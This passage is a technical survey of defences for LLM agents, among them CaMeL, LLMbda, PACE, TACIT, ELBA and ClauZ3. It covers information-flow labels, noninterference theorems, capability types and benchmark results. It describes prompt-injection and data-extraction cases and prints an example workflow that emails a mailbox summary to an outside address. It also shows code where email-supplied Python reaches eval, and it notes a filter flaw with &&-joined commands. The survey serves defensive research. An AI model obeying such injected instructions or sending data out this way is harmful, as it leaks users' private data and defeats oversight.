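The same $g$ appears on both sides, so the condition never compares two different sequences of calls. An agent that emails "yes" if a secret balance exceeds 1,000 euros and "no" otherwise satisfies the condition, because each of the two emails has a fixed text. Costa and colleagues accept this gap because, they argue, full noninterference would in effect forbid every public action after the agent has read a secret. Their model also leaves out timing and the length of network packets, and treats the language model as a deterministic function.

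### Conversations as part of the language

CaMeL and FIDES both build the division between two models into the system. In LLMbda, the agent language of Garby and colleagues, a program creates the division itself with four operations on conversations. `send` adds a message, and `recv` samples the model's answer. `fork` runs an expression on a copy of the conversation and afterwards restores the original. `clear` empties the conversation. With `ask` for a `send` followed by a `recv`, a program can extract an invoice like this (in simplified notation):

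```
inv = fork (clear; ask("Extract payee, account, amount: " + text))
```

| Step | Label of the current conversation |
|---|---|
| Before the line | $T$ |
| `fork` makes a copy | $T$ |
| `clear` empties the copy | $T$ |
| `send` adds the PDF's text | $U$ |
| `recv` returns the invoice, so `inv` is $U$ | $U$ |
| `fork` ends and restores the original | $T$ |

The main conversation is as trusted as before, and the program can go on using it to plan, provided it never sends `inv` there.

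If a model's answer is code, the interpreter runs it immediately, with the program-counter label $pc$ initially set to the label of the conversation that produced it. Code that a model wrote after reading an untrusted PDF therefore runs as if it were inside an untrusted branch, and it cannot call tools that require trusted data. Untrusted branches also cannot change trusted conversations, so the interpreter blocks any `send` to one from inside such a branch.

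### The noninterference theorem

The theorem for LLMbda compares two runs from the viewpoint of an observer at some level $m$, who sees only values whose labels may flow to $m$. To study the influence of untrusted mail, we choose $m$ so that the observer sees only trusted values. Each run starts from a conversation $C$ and a program $e$. Two starting points are indistinguishable, written $\sim_m$, if they differ only in parts the observer cannot see.

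Because a model samples its answers, a program has a probability for each visible result $q$. Call these probabilities $\mu(q)$. They may add up to less than 1, and the missing part is the probability that the run produces no result, either because it never ends or because a policy check stops it. The theorem is

$$(C_0, e_0) \sim_m (C_1, e_1) \;\Rightarrow\; \mu_0 \smile \mu_1 \qquad \text{for every level } m,$$

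where $\mu_0 \smile \mu_1$, read "$\mu_0$ and $\mu_1$ are compatible", means that some $\omega$ satisfies

$$\mu_0(q) \le \omega(q), \quad \mu_1(q) \le \omega(q) \;\text{ for all } q, \qquad \sum_q \omega(q) \le 1.$$

In words, changing the untrusted inputs can change the probabilities of trusted results only if some runs produce no result. The rarer such runs are, the less the probabilities can change. Suppose an agent decides whether to pay the rent today or tomorrow, and the decision counts as trusted. The table shows how the agent behaves with three different emails in the mailbox.

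| Result | Email 1 | Email 2 | Email 3 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Pay today | 0.5 | 0.4 | 0.1 |
| Pay tomorrow | 0.3 | 0.5 | 0.8 |
| No result | 0.2 | 0.1 | 0.1 |

Emails 1 and 2 are compatible. The larger entries in the first two rows are 0.5 and 0.5, which add up to 1, so they can serve as $\omega$. For emails 1 and 3, the larger entries are 0.5 and 0.8, which add up to 1.3. No $\omega$ exists, so the theorem rules out any program that behaves this way.

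Garby and colleagues also bound the difference between two runs:

$$\tfrac{1}{2}\sum_q |\mu_0(q) - \mu_1(q)| \;\le\; \tfrac{1}{2}\,(\mathrm{div}_0 + \mathrm{div}_1),$$

where $\mathrm{div}$ is the probability of no result. For emails 1 and 2, both sides equal 0.15. If a program always finishes, the right side is zero, and the mail has no influence at all on trusted results.

The proof constructs $\omega$ by running the program with a second interpreter. As soon as a step's label rises above what the observer may see, this interpreter skips the step and substitutes an empty value. Skipping cannot make a visible result less likely, because a skipped step cannot fail to finish. The second interpreter never reads the parts where the two starting points differ, so it produces the same $\omega$ for both.

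The theorem covers even programs that a model has not yet written, but it does not show that a given program will finish its task, since a label check may stop it at `send_payment`. It also assumes that the developer labels the sources correctly and puts a check in every sensitive tool. Finally, it assumes that all data sources are part of the program, but a real mail server is outside it.

None of the three designs analyses a particular plan before running it. They differ in what they settle in advance and in which flows they do not cover.

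| Design | Settled in advance | Enforced during the run | Flows left out |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | The plan for one task, without a soundness theorem | Labels, and policies at tool calls | Skipped branches, retries, string templates |
| FIDES | Explicit secrecy for one planning loop | Labels on messages and variables, policies at tool calls | The choice and order of tool calls, timing |
| LLMbda | Noninterference for all programs without endorsements, checked in Lean | Labels at every step, checks inside the tools | Whether a run produces a result, timing |

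### Endorsement, counted in bits

An agent that pays bills must eventually act on its mail, so somebody must decide which untrusted values it may trust. The bookkeeper can do this by approving each payment, but the approval is reliable only if the screen shows the payment accurately. If a model read the PDF and then wrote the text on the screen, the attacker may have influenced that text, so the harness should display the actual account and amount. Costa and colleagues warn that people asked to confirm many actions stop reading carefully, and that attackers can deceive them.

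A format check is simpler but weaker. If the harness accepts only ten digits as an account number, the value cannot carry an instruction to another model. But an attacker who controls the PDF can still choose any of the $10^{10}$ possible account numbers, which gives them $\log_2 10^{10} \approx 33.2$ bits of control over the payment.

With $n$ permitted answers, the attacker controls at most $\log_2 n$ bits. A yes-or-no answer gives $\log_2 2 = 1$ bit, and a choice among eight vendors gives $\log_2 8 = 3$ bits. If the quarantined model may also answer "none of these", there are nine possible answers, which give about 3.2 bits.

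These limits apply to a single answer, but a program can combine several. Twelve choices among eight options carry 36 bits, which is more than a ten-digit account number needs. A program that assembled the number from twelve such answers would let the attacker choose all of it, much like the program that rebuilt it from a trusted table of digits. Besides limiting each answer, the design therefore has to limit either the number of questions or what the program does with the answers.

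The number of bits also doesn't measure the possible damage. One bit can determine whether the company pays an invoice for 50,000 euros. Three bits can determine which of eight vendors gets the money, and one of those vendors may be the attacker.

LLMbda has an explicit `endorse` operation, which a reviewer can search for in the program. For a value with confidentiality label $c$ and a new integrity label $i'$, the result gets the label

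$$pc \sqcup (c, i').$$

Because the formula includes $pc$, a value endorsed inside a branch that depends on the mail remains untrusted. Garby and colleagues prefer this kind of endorsement to the typed labels in FIDES, where a reviewer who sees a Boolean pass a check cannot tell whether the developer intended that flow.

Endorsing data does not weaken the protection of secrets, because the theorem still holds after an endorsement for an observer at level $(P, U)$, who sees all public values, trusted or not. But the theorem no longer applies to the program for an observer who sees only trusted values, and it does not prevent a program from endorsing an entire email. The bound of $\log_2 n$ bits comes from a separate argument about one program, and it holds only if that program maps the answer to one of $n$ fixed values before endorsing it. Garby and colleagues show that the interpreter can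 enforce such a mapping. It can also forbid further endorsements in code created through endorsed data.

### Results on AgentDojo

To test LLMbda, Garby and colleagues wrote an agent called Randori. It asks a model for a program, tries the program on simulated tools, and returns any errors to the model, repeating this until a version works. Then it runs that version once on the benchmark's own tools. The trials involve no untrusted data, so the planning conversation stays trusted. The model may write endorsements into its program, but only before it has received any outside data.

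They ran the 16 banking tasks of AgentDojo three times each, first without attacks and then with each of nine attacks. They also reran CaMeL for comparison. The table shows how many of the 48 runs without attacks completed their task, and how many attacks succeeded. Some of CaMeL's attacked runs did not complete, so its totals for those runs are smaller.

| Agent | Tasks, GPT-5.2 | Successful attacks | Tasks, MiMo-v2.5 | Successful attacks |
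|---|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | 36 | 2 of 432 | 31 | 0 of 432 |
| Randori without endorsement | not run | not run | 26 | 0 of 432 |
| CaMeL without policies | 32 | 1 of 240 | 34 | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL with policies | 18 | 0 of 231 | 18 | 0 of 357 |

Turning on its policies reduced the number of tasks CaMeL completed by almost half. Randori, with its checks on, completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did without policies. With only 16 different tasks, the margins of error are around 20 percentage points, so smaller differences in the table mean little. Both successful attacks on Randori involved a task to pay a bill described in a text file, which the attacker had replaced. The program endorsed the file's contents because the task required it, and no label could have distinguished the false bill from a real one.

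The labels explain only part of the low attack rates. In 97 of the 144 pairs of task and attack, the attack needs a tool call or a file that no sensible plan for the task would contain, so a plan written in advance defeats it without any labels. Only the other 47 pairs test the labels, and on those CaMeL without policies still stopped all attacks with GPT-5.2 and all but three of 141 with MiMo.

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with older models. With GPT-4o, averaged over the four settings, FIDES completed 50% of the tasks, compared with 42% for the single-label agent and 84% for an agent with neither variables nor checks. With OpenAI's o1, its lead over the single-label agent grew to about 16 percentage points, because o1 was better at handling variables. Every attack that would have broken the policies failed. However, the team had labelled a field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark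 used it, so no attack could arrive through a field with the wrong label. A company that labels its own data doesn't have a list of the fields that attacks will use. The tests also left out the restricted answer types, so they do not show how safe the one-bit exception is in practice. According to Wang and colleagues, the FIDES paper had not been peer reviewed, unlike the one on CaMeL.

Peters-Gill and colleagues tested five newer models on AgentDojo, dividing its tools among several agents and running 949 attacked tasks for each model and design, without policies. On average, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of cases with no defence, in 0.2% when each agent ran CaMeL separately, and in none with multi-CaMeL. Almost all the successes without a defence were against two models, GPT-4.1, where 36.1% of attacks succeeded, and Gemini 2.5 Pro, where 24.6% did. Only 1.5% succeeded against Claude Fable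 5 and none against GPT-5.5, so the benchmark can no longer show much about whether a defence helps the strongest models. Its attacks are also a fixed collection, so GPT-5.5 may still be vulnerable to others.

Planning ahead reduces task completion less as models improve. On AssetOpsBench, a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, CaMeL lowered task completion by an average of 21.6 points over the five models, but by 13.4 points for Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Multi-CaMeL lowered it by another 3.2 points on average, but by less than one point for these two. On the divided AgentDojo, Fable 5 refused 52 of 97 harmless tasks, perhaps because it recognised a security benchmark. The AssetOpsBench figures exclude losses from policies, which were larger than those from planning ahead in the banking tests.

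### Authority instead of origin

CaMeL and FIDES treat tool descriptions as trusted, but agents increasingly load tools and written instructions ("skills") from strangers, and an attacker's text then reaches the planner directly. *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) proves a limit on what a check before installation can achieve in this case. For example, a mail skill's code might always call `send_email(body)`, while an accompanying text tells the model what to put in the body. Two versions of the skill can have the same code and interface, although one text gives the model a harmless template and the other tells it to include confidential data. A check that gets the same evidence for both versions must give both the same verdict, so a sound check cannot exempt even the harmless version from runtime checks.

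PACE therefore examines every tool call immediately before the harness executes it. One part builds a graph of where the agent's data came from and looks for paths from protected or untrusted data to the effect of the call. If it finds one, it proposes an intervention to cut the path, usually by blocking the call. The other part ignores where the values came from and compares the call's effects with what the user has authorised. It derives this authority only from the user's request, with limits on purpose, resources, arguments and budget. No text from a model can extend it. If the bookkeeper has asked for one payment of up to 500 euros to Miller Ltd, the check rejects a payment to anyone else. It would permit much more if the assistant had a standing order to pay all incoming invoices.

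Li and colleagues prove that the proposed cut separates the recorded sources from the effect and that the user has authorised every effect the tool's description lists. They do not claim noninterference, and the record can miss paraphrased text and undeclared side effects. The tested version could also restore a call that the path check had blocked if the user had authorised that call, and the proved separation then no longer held.

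On AgentDojo, the three models had these rates of attack success (for the most successful group of attacks) and task completion:

| Defence | Qwen-3.8-27B | DeepSeek-V4-Flash | GPT-5.6 Luna |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 48.0% / 62.6% | 99.8% / 75.7% | 100% / 73.8% |
| CaMeL | 0.3% / 35.1% | 28.1% / 60.0% | 36.1% / 57.0% |
| PACE | 0.0% / 59.7% | 5.1% / 75.3% | 8.1% / 72.1% |

Across eight benchmarks, PACE had the lowest attack rate in 62 of 79 comparisons and tied for the lowest in 14. In a small search for attacks adapted to the defence, none of 30 attempts succeeded against PACE, while 21 succeeded against the unprotected agent.

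The figures for CaMeL are higher than those of Garby and colleagues and Peters-Gill and colleagues, who found rates of about 1% or less. Part of the difference may come from choosing the worst group of attacks. But CaMeL's model writes its plan before reading the untrusted text, so making that text more persuasive should not help an attack much. The tests may have used a version of CaMeL that worked differently, or they may have counted successes differently. The comparison between PACE and CaMeL deserves little weight until somebody explains the difference.

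Tests of the individual checks are more informative. On a sample of AgentDojo cases with Qwen, attacks succeeded in 37.4% of cases without a defence and in none with either check alone. The authority check alone reduced task completion from 76.8% to 64.6%, while the path check alone reduced it to 13.6%. An agent that may act only on trusted data can do little with its mail, as the single-label agent had already shown. On a sample from another benchmark, AgentDyn, even the full system reduced completion from 66.7% to 33.3%.

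### Secrets and the final judgement

Outsiders can also get secrets out of an agent without prompt injection. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) studied outsiders who just talk to someone's personal agent. Many agents have a rule in their prompt to get the owner's consent before disclosing anything, but the rule works only if the model detects that it is about to disclose something. Against one carefully designed prompt with such a rule, earlier attacks had extracted 1.9% to 3.0% of the protected items, while requests that looked like ordinary collaboration extracted 43.8% to 75.6%.

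Their defence, FlowSeal, no longer leaves the model to decide whether to apply the rule. Each sensitive record is labelled with its owner, based on where the record came from. A component outside the conversation intercepts every call that writes or shares data, tracks the labels and classifies the destination. If protected data might leave, a separate model call compares the protected records with the proposed text and decides whether to release the text. This call does not receive the conversation, so the outsider cannot argue with it.

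Across the tests, FlowSeal limited the loss to between 0% and 3.3% of protected items and completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best prompt-based defence. Shim and colleagues prove that the labels stop protected data from moving to a less protected place, except through the release decision. They exclude prompt injection from their study. An attacker who could place instructions in the proposed text might influence the model that judges it, and the proof does not protect against a wrong judgement.

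## Can programs written by the model be checked before they run?

CaMeL's privileged model writes a whole program before the mail arrives, but the interpreter detects a forbidden flow only when execution reaches it. A harness can instead check the program before it runs, as in Zhou and colleagues' calculator example. The harness gives the model a list of functions the program may call and a type or policy it must satisfy. A checker with no language model in it then accepts the program or returns it to the model with an error message. A rejected program delays the task but has no other effects, because it never runs.

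The idea goes back to "proof-carrying code", developed in the 1990s. The supplier of a program also provides evidence that it is safe, and the recipient checks the evidence before running the program. Finding a proof can be hard, but checking one is mechanical, so the recipient doesn't have to trust the supplier. AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026), a write-up of a talk by Erik Meijer, adds that the checker must be able to read the program's structure. If a harness delays a program but can't read its structure, it has no basis for deciding whether to stop it.

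### A mail summary with a hidden copy

In *Guardians of the Agents* (2025), Meijer gives the example of a user who asks an agent to fetch and summarise her emails. One email claims that, for legal compliance, the assistant must send a summary of the mailbox to an outside address without mentioning it. An ordinary agent with the tools `fetch_mail` and `send_email` may well obey. In Meijer's design, the model writes its workflow before it reads any mail, so the email cannot add a step.

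The same instruction can still reach the model earlier, for example in a tool description that a stranger wrote. The model might then produce this workflow (in simplified notation):

```
1  mails   = fetch_mail()
2  summary = summarize(mails)
3  send_email(to="audit@outside.example", body=summary)
4  return summary
```

Meijer's policy forbids data from `fetch_mail` (the source) from reaching the body of `send_email` (the sink) if the recipient is outside the company's domain. The checker marks `mails` at line 1 and `summary` at line 2, because `summary` depends on `mails`. At line 3 it finds `summary` in the body and a constant address outside the domain in `to`, so the harness rejects the workflow before it fetches any email. Without line 3, the workflow passes. If the recipient were a variable whose value the checker could not determine, a sound checker would also have to reject the workflow,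 unless the program tested the address first.

Meijer suggests CodeQL or Semgrep, two existing tools that search code for such paths. He describes a design but reports no experiments, and he concedes that nobody has formally measured how writing a plan first affects an agent's performance.

The usual alternative is to ask the user before each tool call. Frequent requests make people careless, and even a careful reader often cannot judge them. normalform-ai's *ClauZ3*, which presents an open-source checker for agents' Python programs, shows a script of about 20 lines that is supposed to email Bob about a software update but also emails everyone on a list in the computer's settings. The user who has to approve the script cannot see who is on that list. Automatic rules about commands are fragile as well. Zhou and colleagues cite a fault from March 2026 in which Claude Code checked only the first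 of several commands joined by `&&` against its list of forbidden commands.

A monitor could block the email at line 3. Meijer objects that by then the agent has already retrieved and processed private mail. The objection is weak here, because the user asked the agent to do that and the summary would never have left the company. Checking in advance matters more when earlier steps are hard to undo, for example when a program makes four payments before a fifth breaks a rule.

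### Effects and capabilities in types

A type checker can check the model's program before it runs if each function's type lists what the function may do to the outside world. One way to list these effects is with capabilities, which are values that a program must hold to perform certain actions. In the notation below, `A ->{c} B` is the type of a function that takes an `A`, returns a `B` and may use the capability `c`. A plain arrow means that the function is pure, which means it uses no capabilities.

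```
fetch_mail : ()              ->{inbox}   Mails
summarize  : Mails           ->          Text
send_email : (Address, Text) ->{mailer}  ()
```

Suppose the harness asks for a program of type `() ->{inbox} Text`. The model might write either of these:

```
accepted:   mails = fetch_mail()
            summarize(mails)

rejected:   mails = fetch_mail()
            summary = summarize(mails)
            send_email("audit@outside.example", summary)
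            summary
```

The checker takes the union of the capabilities that the steps use and compares it with the permitted set:

$$\{\text{inbox}\} \cup \emptyset \subseteq \{\text{inbox}\}, \qquad \{\text{inbox}\} \cup \emptyset \cup \{\text{mailer}\} \cup \emptyset \not\subseteq \{\text{inbox}\}.$$

The second program does not compile. For an `if`, the checker includes the capabilities of both branches, so it catches the call even in a branch that rarely runs. The model also cannot create its own `mailer`, provided the language has no way to forge one.

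This type forbids all outgoing email, which is too strict for an agent that also has to answer letters. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, allow an agent to hold `mailer` while keeping it away from secrets. Their system, TACIT, has agents write programs in Scala 3, whose experimental "capture checking" records in a value's type which capabilities the value can reach. Files in protected folders arrive inside a wrapper called `Classified`. The agent can work on the contents only by passing a function to the wrapper's `map` method, and `map` accepts only pure functions. If `registry` is a classified list of suppliers' bank details, the checker decides as follows:

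```
registry.map(r => find_account(r, "Miller"))     accepted
registry.map(r => send_email(stranger, r))       rejected
```

The first function is pure, but its result is still `Classified`, so the agent can't send it. The second uses `mailer`, so it is not pure. This design also handles the implicit flows that made taint tracking difficult. A program can branch on a secret only inside `map`, where it has no capability that could reveal which branch it took.

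### What TACIT checks, and when

TACIT treats the cloud model that runs the agent as a possible attacker, so the model's conversation must never contain a secret. When the agent prints a classified value, the model receives only asterisks, while the user sees the contents on a separate screen. If a task needs a language model to process the secret, for example to summarise an incident report, the program passes the classified text to a trusted local model, whose answer is also classified.

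The type checker also limits how long a capability lasts. A program that needs files requests access to one folder for one block of code, and no value that leaves the block may contain the capability. An agent therefore cannot return a function that reads `secret.txt` after the block ends. The runtime enforces the rules that types cannot check, rejecting paths outside the folder and any web host or command that is not on an allowed list. It also turns exceptions into ordinary values, because an exception could carry information out of a pure function.

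Researchers have proved the underlying type system sound, with computer-checked proofs. Agents must use a restricted "safe mode" of Scala, which forbids features such as unchecked casts and reflection. Odersky and colleagues say that a further argument is needed to show that safe mode has its intended properties. The design does not cover leaks through timing, and the type checker does not check permitted outside commands at all.

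The main test used a software project with a folder of secrets. Twelve harmless tasks, each combined with ten injections, made 120 trials. In another 11 trials, the user made a malicious request for secrets, five times openly and six times while posing as someone with authority, such as a system administrator. With the wrapper, neither Claude Sonnet 4.6 nor MiniMax M2.5 leaked a secret in any trial. Without it, Sonnet leaked in two trials and MiniMax in 11. Sonnet resisted all 120 injections without the wrapper, so for that model only the malicious requests tested the types. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the harmless tasks with the wrapper and 83.3% without it, while MiniMax completed 90.0% with it and 88.3% without. Sonnet's lower score without the wrapper may be an artefact, because it often ran out of time.

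Writing typed programs did not make the agents noticeably worse. On τ²-bench, a newer version of the customer-service benchmark τ-bench, three models scored between 0.8 and 3.7 percentage points higher than with ordinary tool calls. On SWE-bench Lite, which tests repairs of real software faults, MiniMax scored 41.7% with typed programs and 43.3% without them. At most 8% of the τ²-bench programs needed a retry, and most of those compiled after one or two. The agents could use all the tools in these tests, so the scores reflect the effect of writing Scala but not the effect of a policy that forbids some actions.

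TACIT protects secrets better than it protects the agent's decisions from manipulation. A prompt injection can still cause the agent to write a new program, which will compile if it uses only capabilities the agent holds. An agent with the capability to make payments could therefore pay a false invoice. When Odersky and colleagues adapted AgentDojo to TACIT, TACIT blocked every injection except one.

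### Haskell types as policies

Zhou and colleagues use types to control where data come from as well as what a program does. In their example, an agent compiles a bibliography, and every entry it writes must come from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. Their library offers three functions:

```
dblpSearch      : Text        ->{BibIO}  List of DOI
dblpFetchBib    : DOI         ->{BibIO}  Trusted Bib
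appendToBibFile : Trusted Bib ->{BibIO}  ()
```

The library hides the constructor of `Trusted`, so a program can get a `Trusted Bib` only from `dblpFetchBib`. The program also cannot write to the file another way, because Haskell's general file functions have the effect `IO` and the program must have the effect `BibIO`. The agent can sort and filter the entries, but it cannot add one that it invented.

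In 100 tasks with Claude Sonnet 5, this agent wrote 925 citations, none of which had a wrong author, year or DOI. An ordinary agent with web search got 19 of 1,002 wrong. The comparison does not isolate the effect of the types, because only the first agent could copy whole entries from DBLP. The types also don't ensure that the cited publications are relevant.

Their theorem shows that guarantees like this one survive when programs call agents. Let $L$ be a typed language and $L_{\text{agent}}$ the same language with an added operation that asks a model for a program, type-checks it and runs it. Let $\mathrm{traces}(e)$ be the sequences of outside effects that program $e$ can have. For every type $t$ and property $P$,

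$$\big(\forall e \in L:\; e : t \Rightarrow P(\mathrm{traces}(e))\big) \;\Rightarrow\; \big(\forall e \in L_{\text{agent}}:\; e : t \Rightarrow P(\mathrm{traces}(e))\big).$$

Zhou and colleagues prove the theorem by replacing each call to an agent with an ordinary function of $L$ that queries the model, checks the answer and evaluates it. The result is a well-typed program of $L$ with the same traces, so it has the property. If the model's program calls further agents, the same replacement applies, by induction on the permitted depth of such calls. The theorem extends to agents only the guarantees that the language and its libraries already provide. If somebody adds an unsafe function to the `BibIO` library, agents can use it too.

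The system, called ELBA, checks information flow using LIO, an existing Haskell library. Before the run, the type checker proves that the program acts only through LIO's operations. During the run, LIO keeps a label that rises as the program reads untrusted data, and it throws an error if the program then tries something the label does not allow. A program that passes the type checker can therefore still fail partway through, as a CaMeL program can.

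Zhou and colleagues tested this on AgentDojo's Slack tasks. No attack succeeded against any of the four models, even without policies. But automated attackers are improving (OpenAI's GPT-Red consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences), so the team simulated the worst case by making subagents carry out every injected instruction they read. For each model, they ran 735 attacked tasks with policies and 735 without.

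| Model | Attacks resisted without policies | With policies | Tasks completed without policies | With policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 57.8% | 100% | 71.2% | 47.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 62.6% | 100% | 75.8% | 42.4% |
| GPT 5.4 | 84.5% | 100% | 75.9% | 46.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 73.5% | 100% | 67.2% | 40.0% |

This is a better test of the defence than the usual attacks, because the result does not depend on how easily the models are fooled. The policies lowered every model's task completion rate by more than 20 percentage points. Type errors mattered much less, and models failed to produce a well-typed program within the permitted retries in only seven of 2,688 runs.

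### The order of effects

A set of effects does not record their order, so an agent that asks for approval and then pays has the same set as one that pays and then asks. *ETAS* (Tan, Wang and colleagues, 2026) presents a language whose compiler also checks the order of an agent program's requests.

For each function, the compiler works out a summary of the sequences of requests the function can make. Let $g$ be a request for approval, $p$ a payment and $\varepsilon$ the empty sequence. A Payer that asks for approval and then either pays or does nothing has the summary

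$$A = g\,(\varepsilon \mid p).$$

The rule that no payment may come before a request for approval permits the sequences

$$P = \varepsilon \mid g\,(g \mid p)^*,$$

where the star means "any number of times". A run may stop at any point, so the compiler has to check every beginning of every sequence in $A$. These are $\varepsilon$, $g$ and $gp$, and all three are in $P$. The program therefore satisfies the rule. If the Payer pays first, its summary is $pg$, which begins with $p$, and the compiler rejects it.

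Many programs fall between these cases. If one branch asks first and another pays first, ETAS accepts the program but attaches a monitor that stops the run if it takes the branch that pays first. The compiler can therefore accept an ETAS program without proving that the program follows its rules.

A function's summary covers the functions and agents it calls, because approval requirements are easily lost when an agent delegates work. Tan and colleagues cite a fault report about the coding agent Goose, in which a main agent had to ask before using certain tools but its subagent used them without asking. The summaries also include requests that never leave the program. If a developer runs the Payer in preview mode, a handler intercepts the payment and no money moves. Ordinary effect types would omit this payment, but ETAS keeps it in the summary, so a preview can't hide an unapproved payment.

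The rule $P$ requires the program to request approval but not to receive it, and one request is enough for any number of payments. The program therefore needs an `if` to check the answer, and the host system has to check during the run that the approval covers the particular payment. Tan and colleagues prove that if every effect passes through the language's runtime, every run obeys its order rules and outside effects stay within the declared set.

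Their safety tests are small. Part of a coding agent behaved as expected in ten scripted scenarios, and the compiler gave the right verdict on six short programs, four of them deliberately faulty. The checks therefore work on simple cases, but the tests don't measure how many realistic programs the compiler can prove safe without a monitor.

In another experiment, an agent's own instructions and code went through five rounds of revision, and the compiler checked each version against fixed types and rules before it ran. Accuracy on 256 financial questions rose from 69.9% to 78.9%. The experiment had no comparison group without the checks, so it shows that an agent can improve under the checks, but not whether the checks slow it down or prevent harm.

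### Contracts and solvers

Unlike types with effects, a logical contract can add up payments, because it can state any condition that a solver can check. In ClauZ3, the agent attaches promises to its program, and the solver Z3 searches for a run that would break them.

```
promise: max_spend(5)

withdraw("checking", 2); withdraw("checking", 3)     proved
withdraw("checking", 2); withdraw("checking", 4)     refused
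```

If Z3 finds a violation, the program does not run, and the user is not told about it. If Z3 proves the promises, the user sees only those promises, such as "emails only bob@example.com", and approves or rejects them without reading the code. For a loop over a database, ClauZ3 can also prove that every recipient comes from the email column of the user table.

It makes more sense to ask a user this than to ask whether to run an unfamiliar script. But the agent chooses what to promise, and a promise to email only Bob does not restrict what the email contains. ClauZ3 reduces the problem by letting developers list required and recommended promises, and the approval screen shows which recommended ones are missing. The agent can also declare that it guarantees nothing, and if the user accepts, the program runs with only run-time checks. normalform-ai demonstrates the tool on email and banking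 examples, reports no measurements, and still plans a stronger sandbox. Contracts can also be too weak in less obvious ways, as in Meijer's example of a program that deletes all text files when the user wanted to delete two.

*VeriGuard* (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025) verifies a guard that checks the agent's actions, rather than the agent's program. A model turns a security rule in plain English into a Python function that decides whether an action is allowed, together with formal conditions on that function. If the rule is ambiguous, the model asks the user or, if nobody is available, chooses the most plausible reading. After some tests, the verifier Nagini tries to prove that the function meets the formal conditions. If the proof fails, the model attempts a repair. The finished function checks each action while the agent works and may block the action, end the task or ask the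 agent for a new plan.

The proof covers what the function does with its arguments, but a language model supplies those arguments by reading the agent's data. Suppose the function allows a payment only if `supplier_known` is true. If the model wrongly fills in "true" for an unknown supplier, the verified function allows the payment. The proof also wouldn't detect a mistake in translating the English rule into formal conditions, so the user or a test would have to catch it.

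*Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* applies the same approach to skills, which combine instructions for a model with scripts. Each skill declares a set $D$ of capabilities, such as reading files or using the network. The proposal calls a skill contained if

$$\Pi(\tau) \subseteq D$$

for every run $\tau$, where $\Pi(\tau)$ is the set of capabilities that appear in the run. It treats the two halves of a skill differently. For the scripts, a static analyser computes every effect they could have and compares the result with $D$. The instructions work through a language model, which nobody can analyse in this way, so the runtime has to intercept each tool call and reject any that needs an undeclared capability.

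A third method searches for violations across sequences of calls. With ten declared capabilities, plus one symbol for everything else, there are $11^8$ sequences of eight calls, or about 214 million, which a computer can cover. The skill includes the evidence, and the runtime rechecks it at startup. The proposal comes from a single author, who demonstrates the software on a sample skill. Containment is also a modest goal, because a skill that declares access to email and payments can pay a fraudster and still be contained.

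### Reacting to what the agent learns

The main objection to checking a whole program in advance is that the program can't use what the agent learns while it runs. In the earlier example of a PDF that needs a password from a second email, a plan fails if it doesn't include a step to get the password. Meijer's workflows have this weakness because the model must write them before it reads any data.

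One reply is that a plan can contain branches. For example, it can look for a password and, if there is one, use it to open the file. The proof still works because it covers every possible result of each step. AI Engineer gives an example in the proof language Lean, in which a plan reads a file and then continues differently depending on the contents. Proving that the plan deletes nothing requires showing that the continuation deletes nothing, whatever the file contains. Branches are enough for events that the model can foresee, but they do not help when a document raises a question nobody expected.

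Zhou and colleagues let the program call a subagent at that point. Their bibliography agent can search DBLP, put the first result into a new prompt and ask a subagent to continue. The subagent writes its own program after seeing the result. The call appears where the checker requires a `BibIO` program, so the subagent's program must also have that type. The parent may impose a stricter type, but not a looser one.

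TACIT gets a similar effect by checking each new program in a conversation separately. Capabilities from an earlier program have expired by then, and classified values stay wrapped.

The evidence that this flexibility helps is mixed. Across the four models, ELBA completed 37 of the 84 Slack tasks without attacks when its policies were on, and CaMeL completed 20. Without policies, ELBA completed 64 and CaMeL 61, so the freedom to write new programs made little difference by itself. The larger gap with policies on may come partly from differences between the two systems' policies. When the data contained attacks, ELBA completed 81% of tasks without policies and CaMeL completed 69%. ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL, mainly because it called the model more often.

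Letting the model write programs after it has read untrusted text also gives up some protection. An email cannot add a payment to a plan that was fixed before the email arrived, even if the policy would allow the payment. But if the model writes its next program after reading the email, the email can influence that program, and the checker stops only what the policy forbids. The policy then has to exclude harms that a fixed plan would have prevented. ELBA's labels prevent some of these harms, because a subagent that has read untrusted text can no longer use sensitive tools. A plain list of capabilities does not add this restriction, because it stays the same whatever the agent has read.

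Checking each program separately can also miss a limit that applies to the whole task. Suppose the user allows an agent to spend five euros, and the agent writes two programs that each spend four. Each program satisfies `max_spend(5)`, but together they spend eight. The harness has to subtract the first program's spending from the limit before it checks the second.

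## What does it mean when a scanner finds no taint flow in an agent's code?

A type checker can rule out forbidden effects in a model's program because the harness chooses the language the model writes in. But developers wrote most existing agents in ordinary Python or TypeScript, and most static tools for these agents look for faults but don't try to prove there are none. When such a tool reports no taint flow, the code may have none, or it may have one that the tool could not follow.

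### A missed flow and a false alarm

Suppose the company adds these lines to its invoice assistant. Python's `eval` runs a string as code, which makes it a dangerous sink.

```
 1  class Discount:
 2      def run(self, text):
 3          return eval(text)
 4
 5  tools = load_tools("tools.json")
 6
 7  def answer(mail):
 8      reply = model(INSTRUCTIONS + mail)
 9      return tools[reply.tool].run(reply.text)
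10
11  def add_tax(mail):
12      amount = int(model("Extract the amount: " + mail))
13      return eval(f"{amount} * 1.19")
```

Someone can send an email that asks for the discount tool and supplies a line of Python that deletes the ledger. If the model passes that code on, the assistant runs it. To find this flow, an analyser has to connect the call at line 9 with the function at line 2. But the tool's name comes from the model's reply, and the list of tools comes from a file the program reads at startup. An analyser that doesn't connect the two lines finds no path from the email to line 3 and reports nothing.

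The other function, `add_tax`, is harmless because `int` raises an error unless the model's answer is a whole number, so line 13 can only multiply two numbers. An analyser that labels every result with the join of its inputs' labels still reports line 13, because `amount` depends on the mail.

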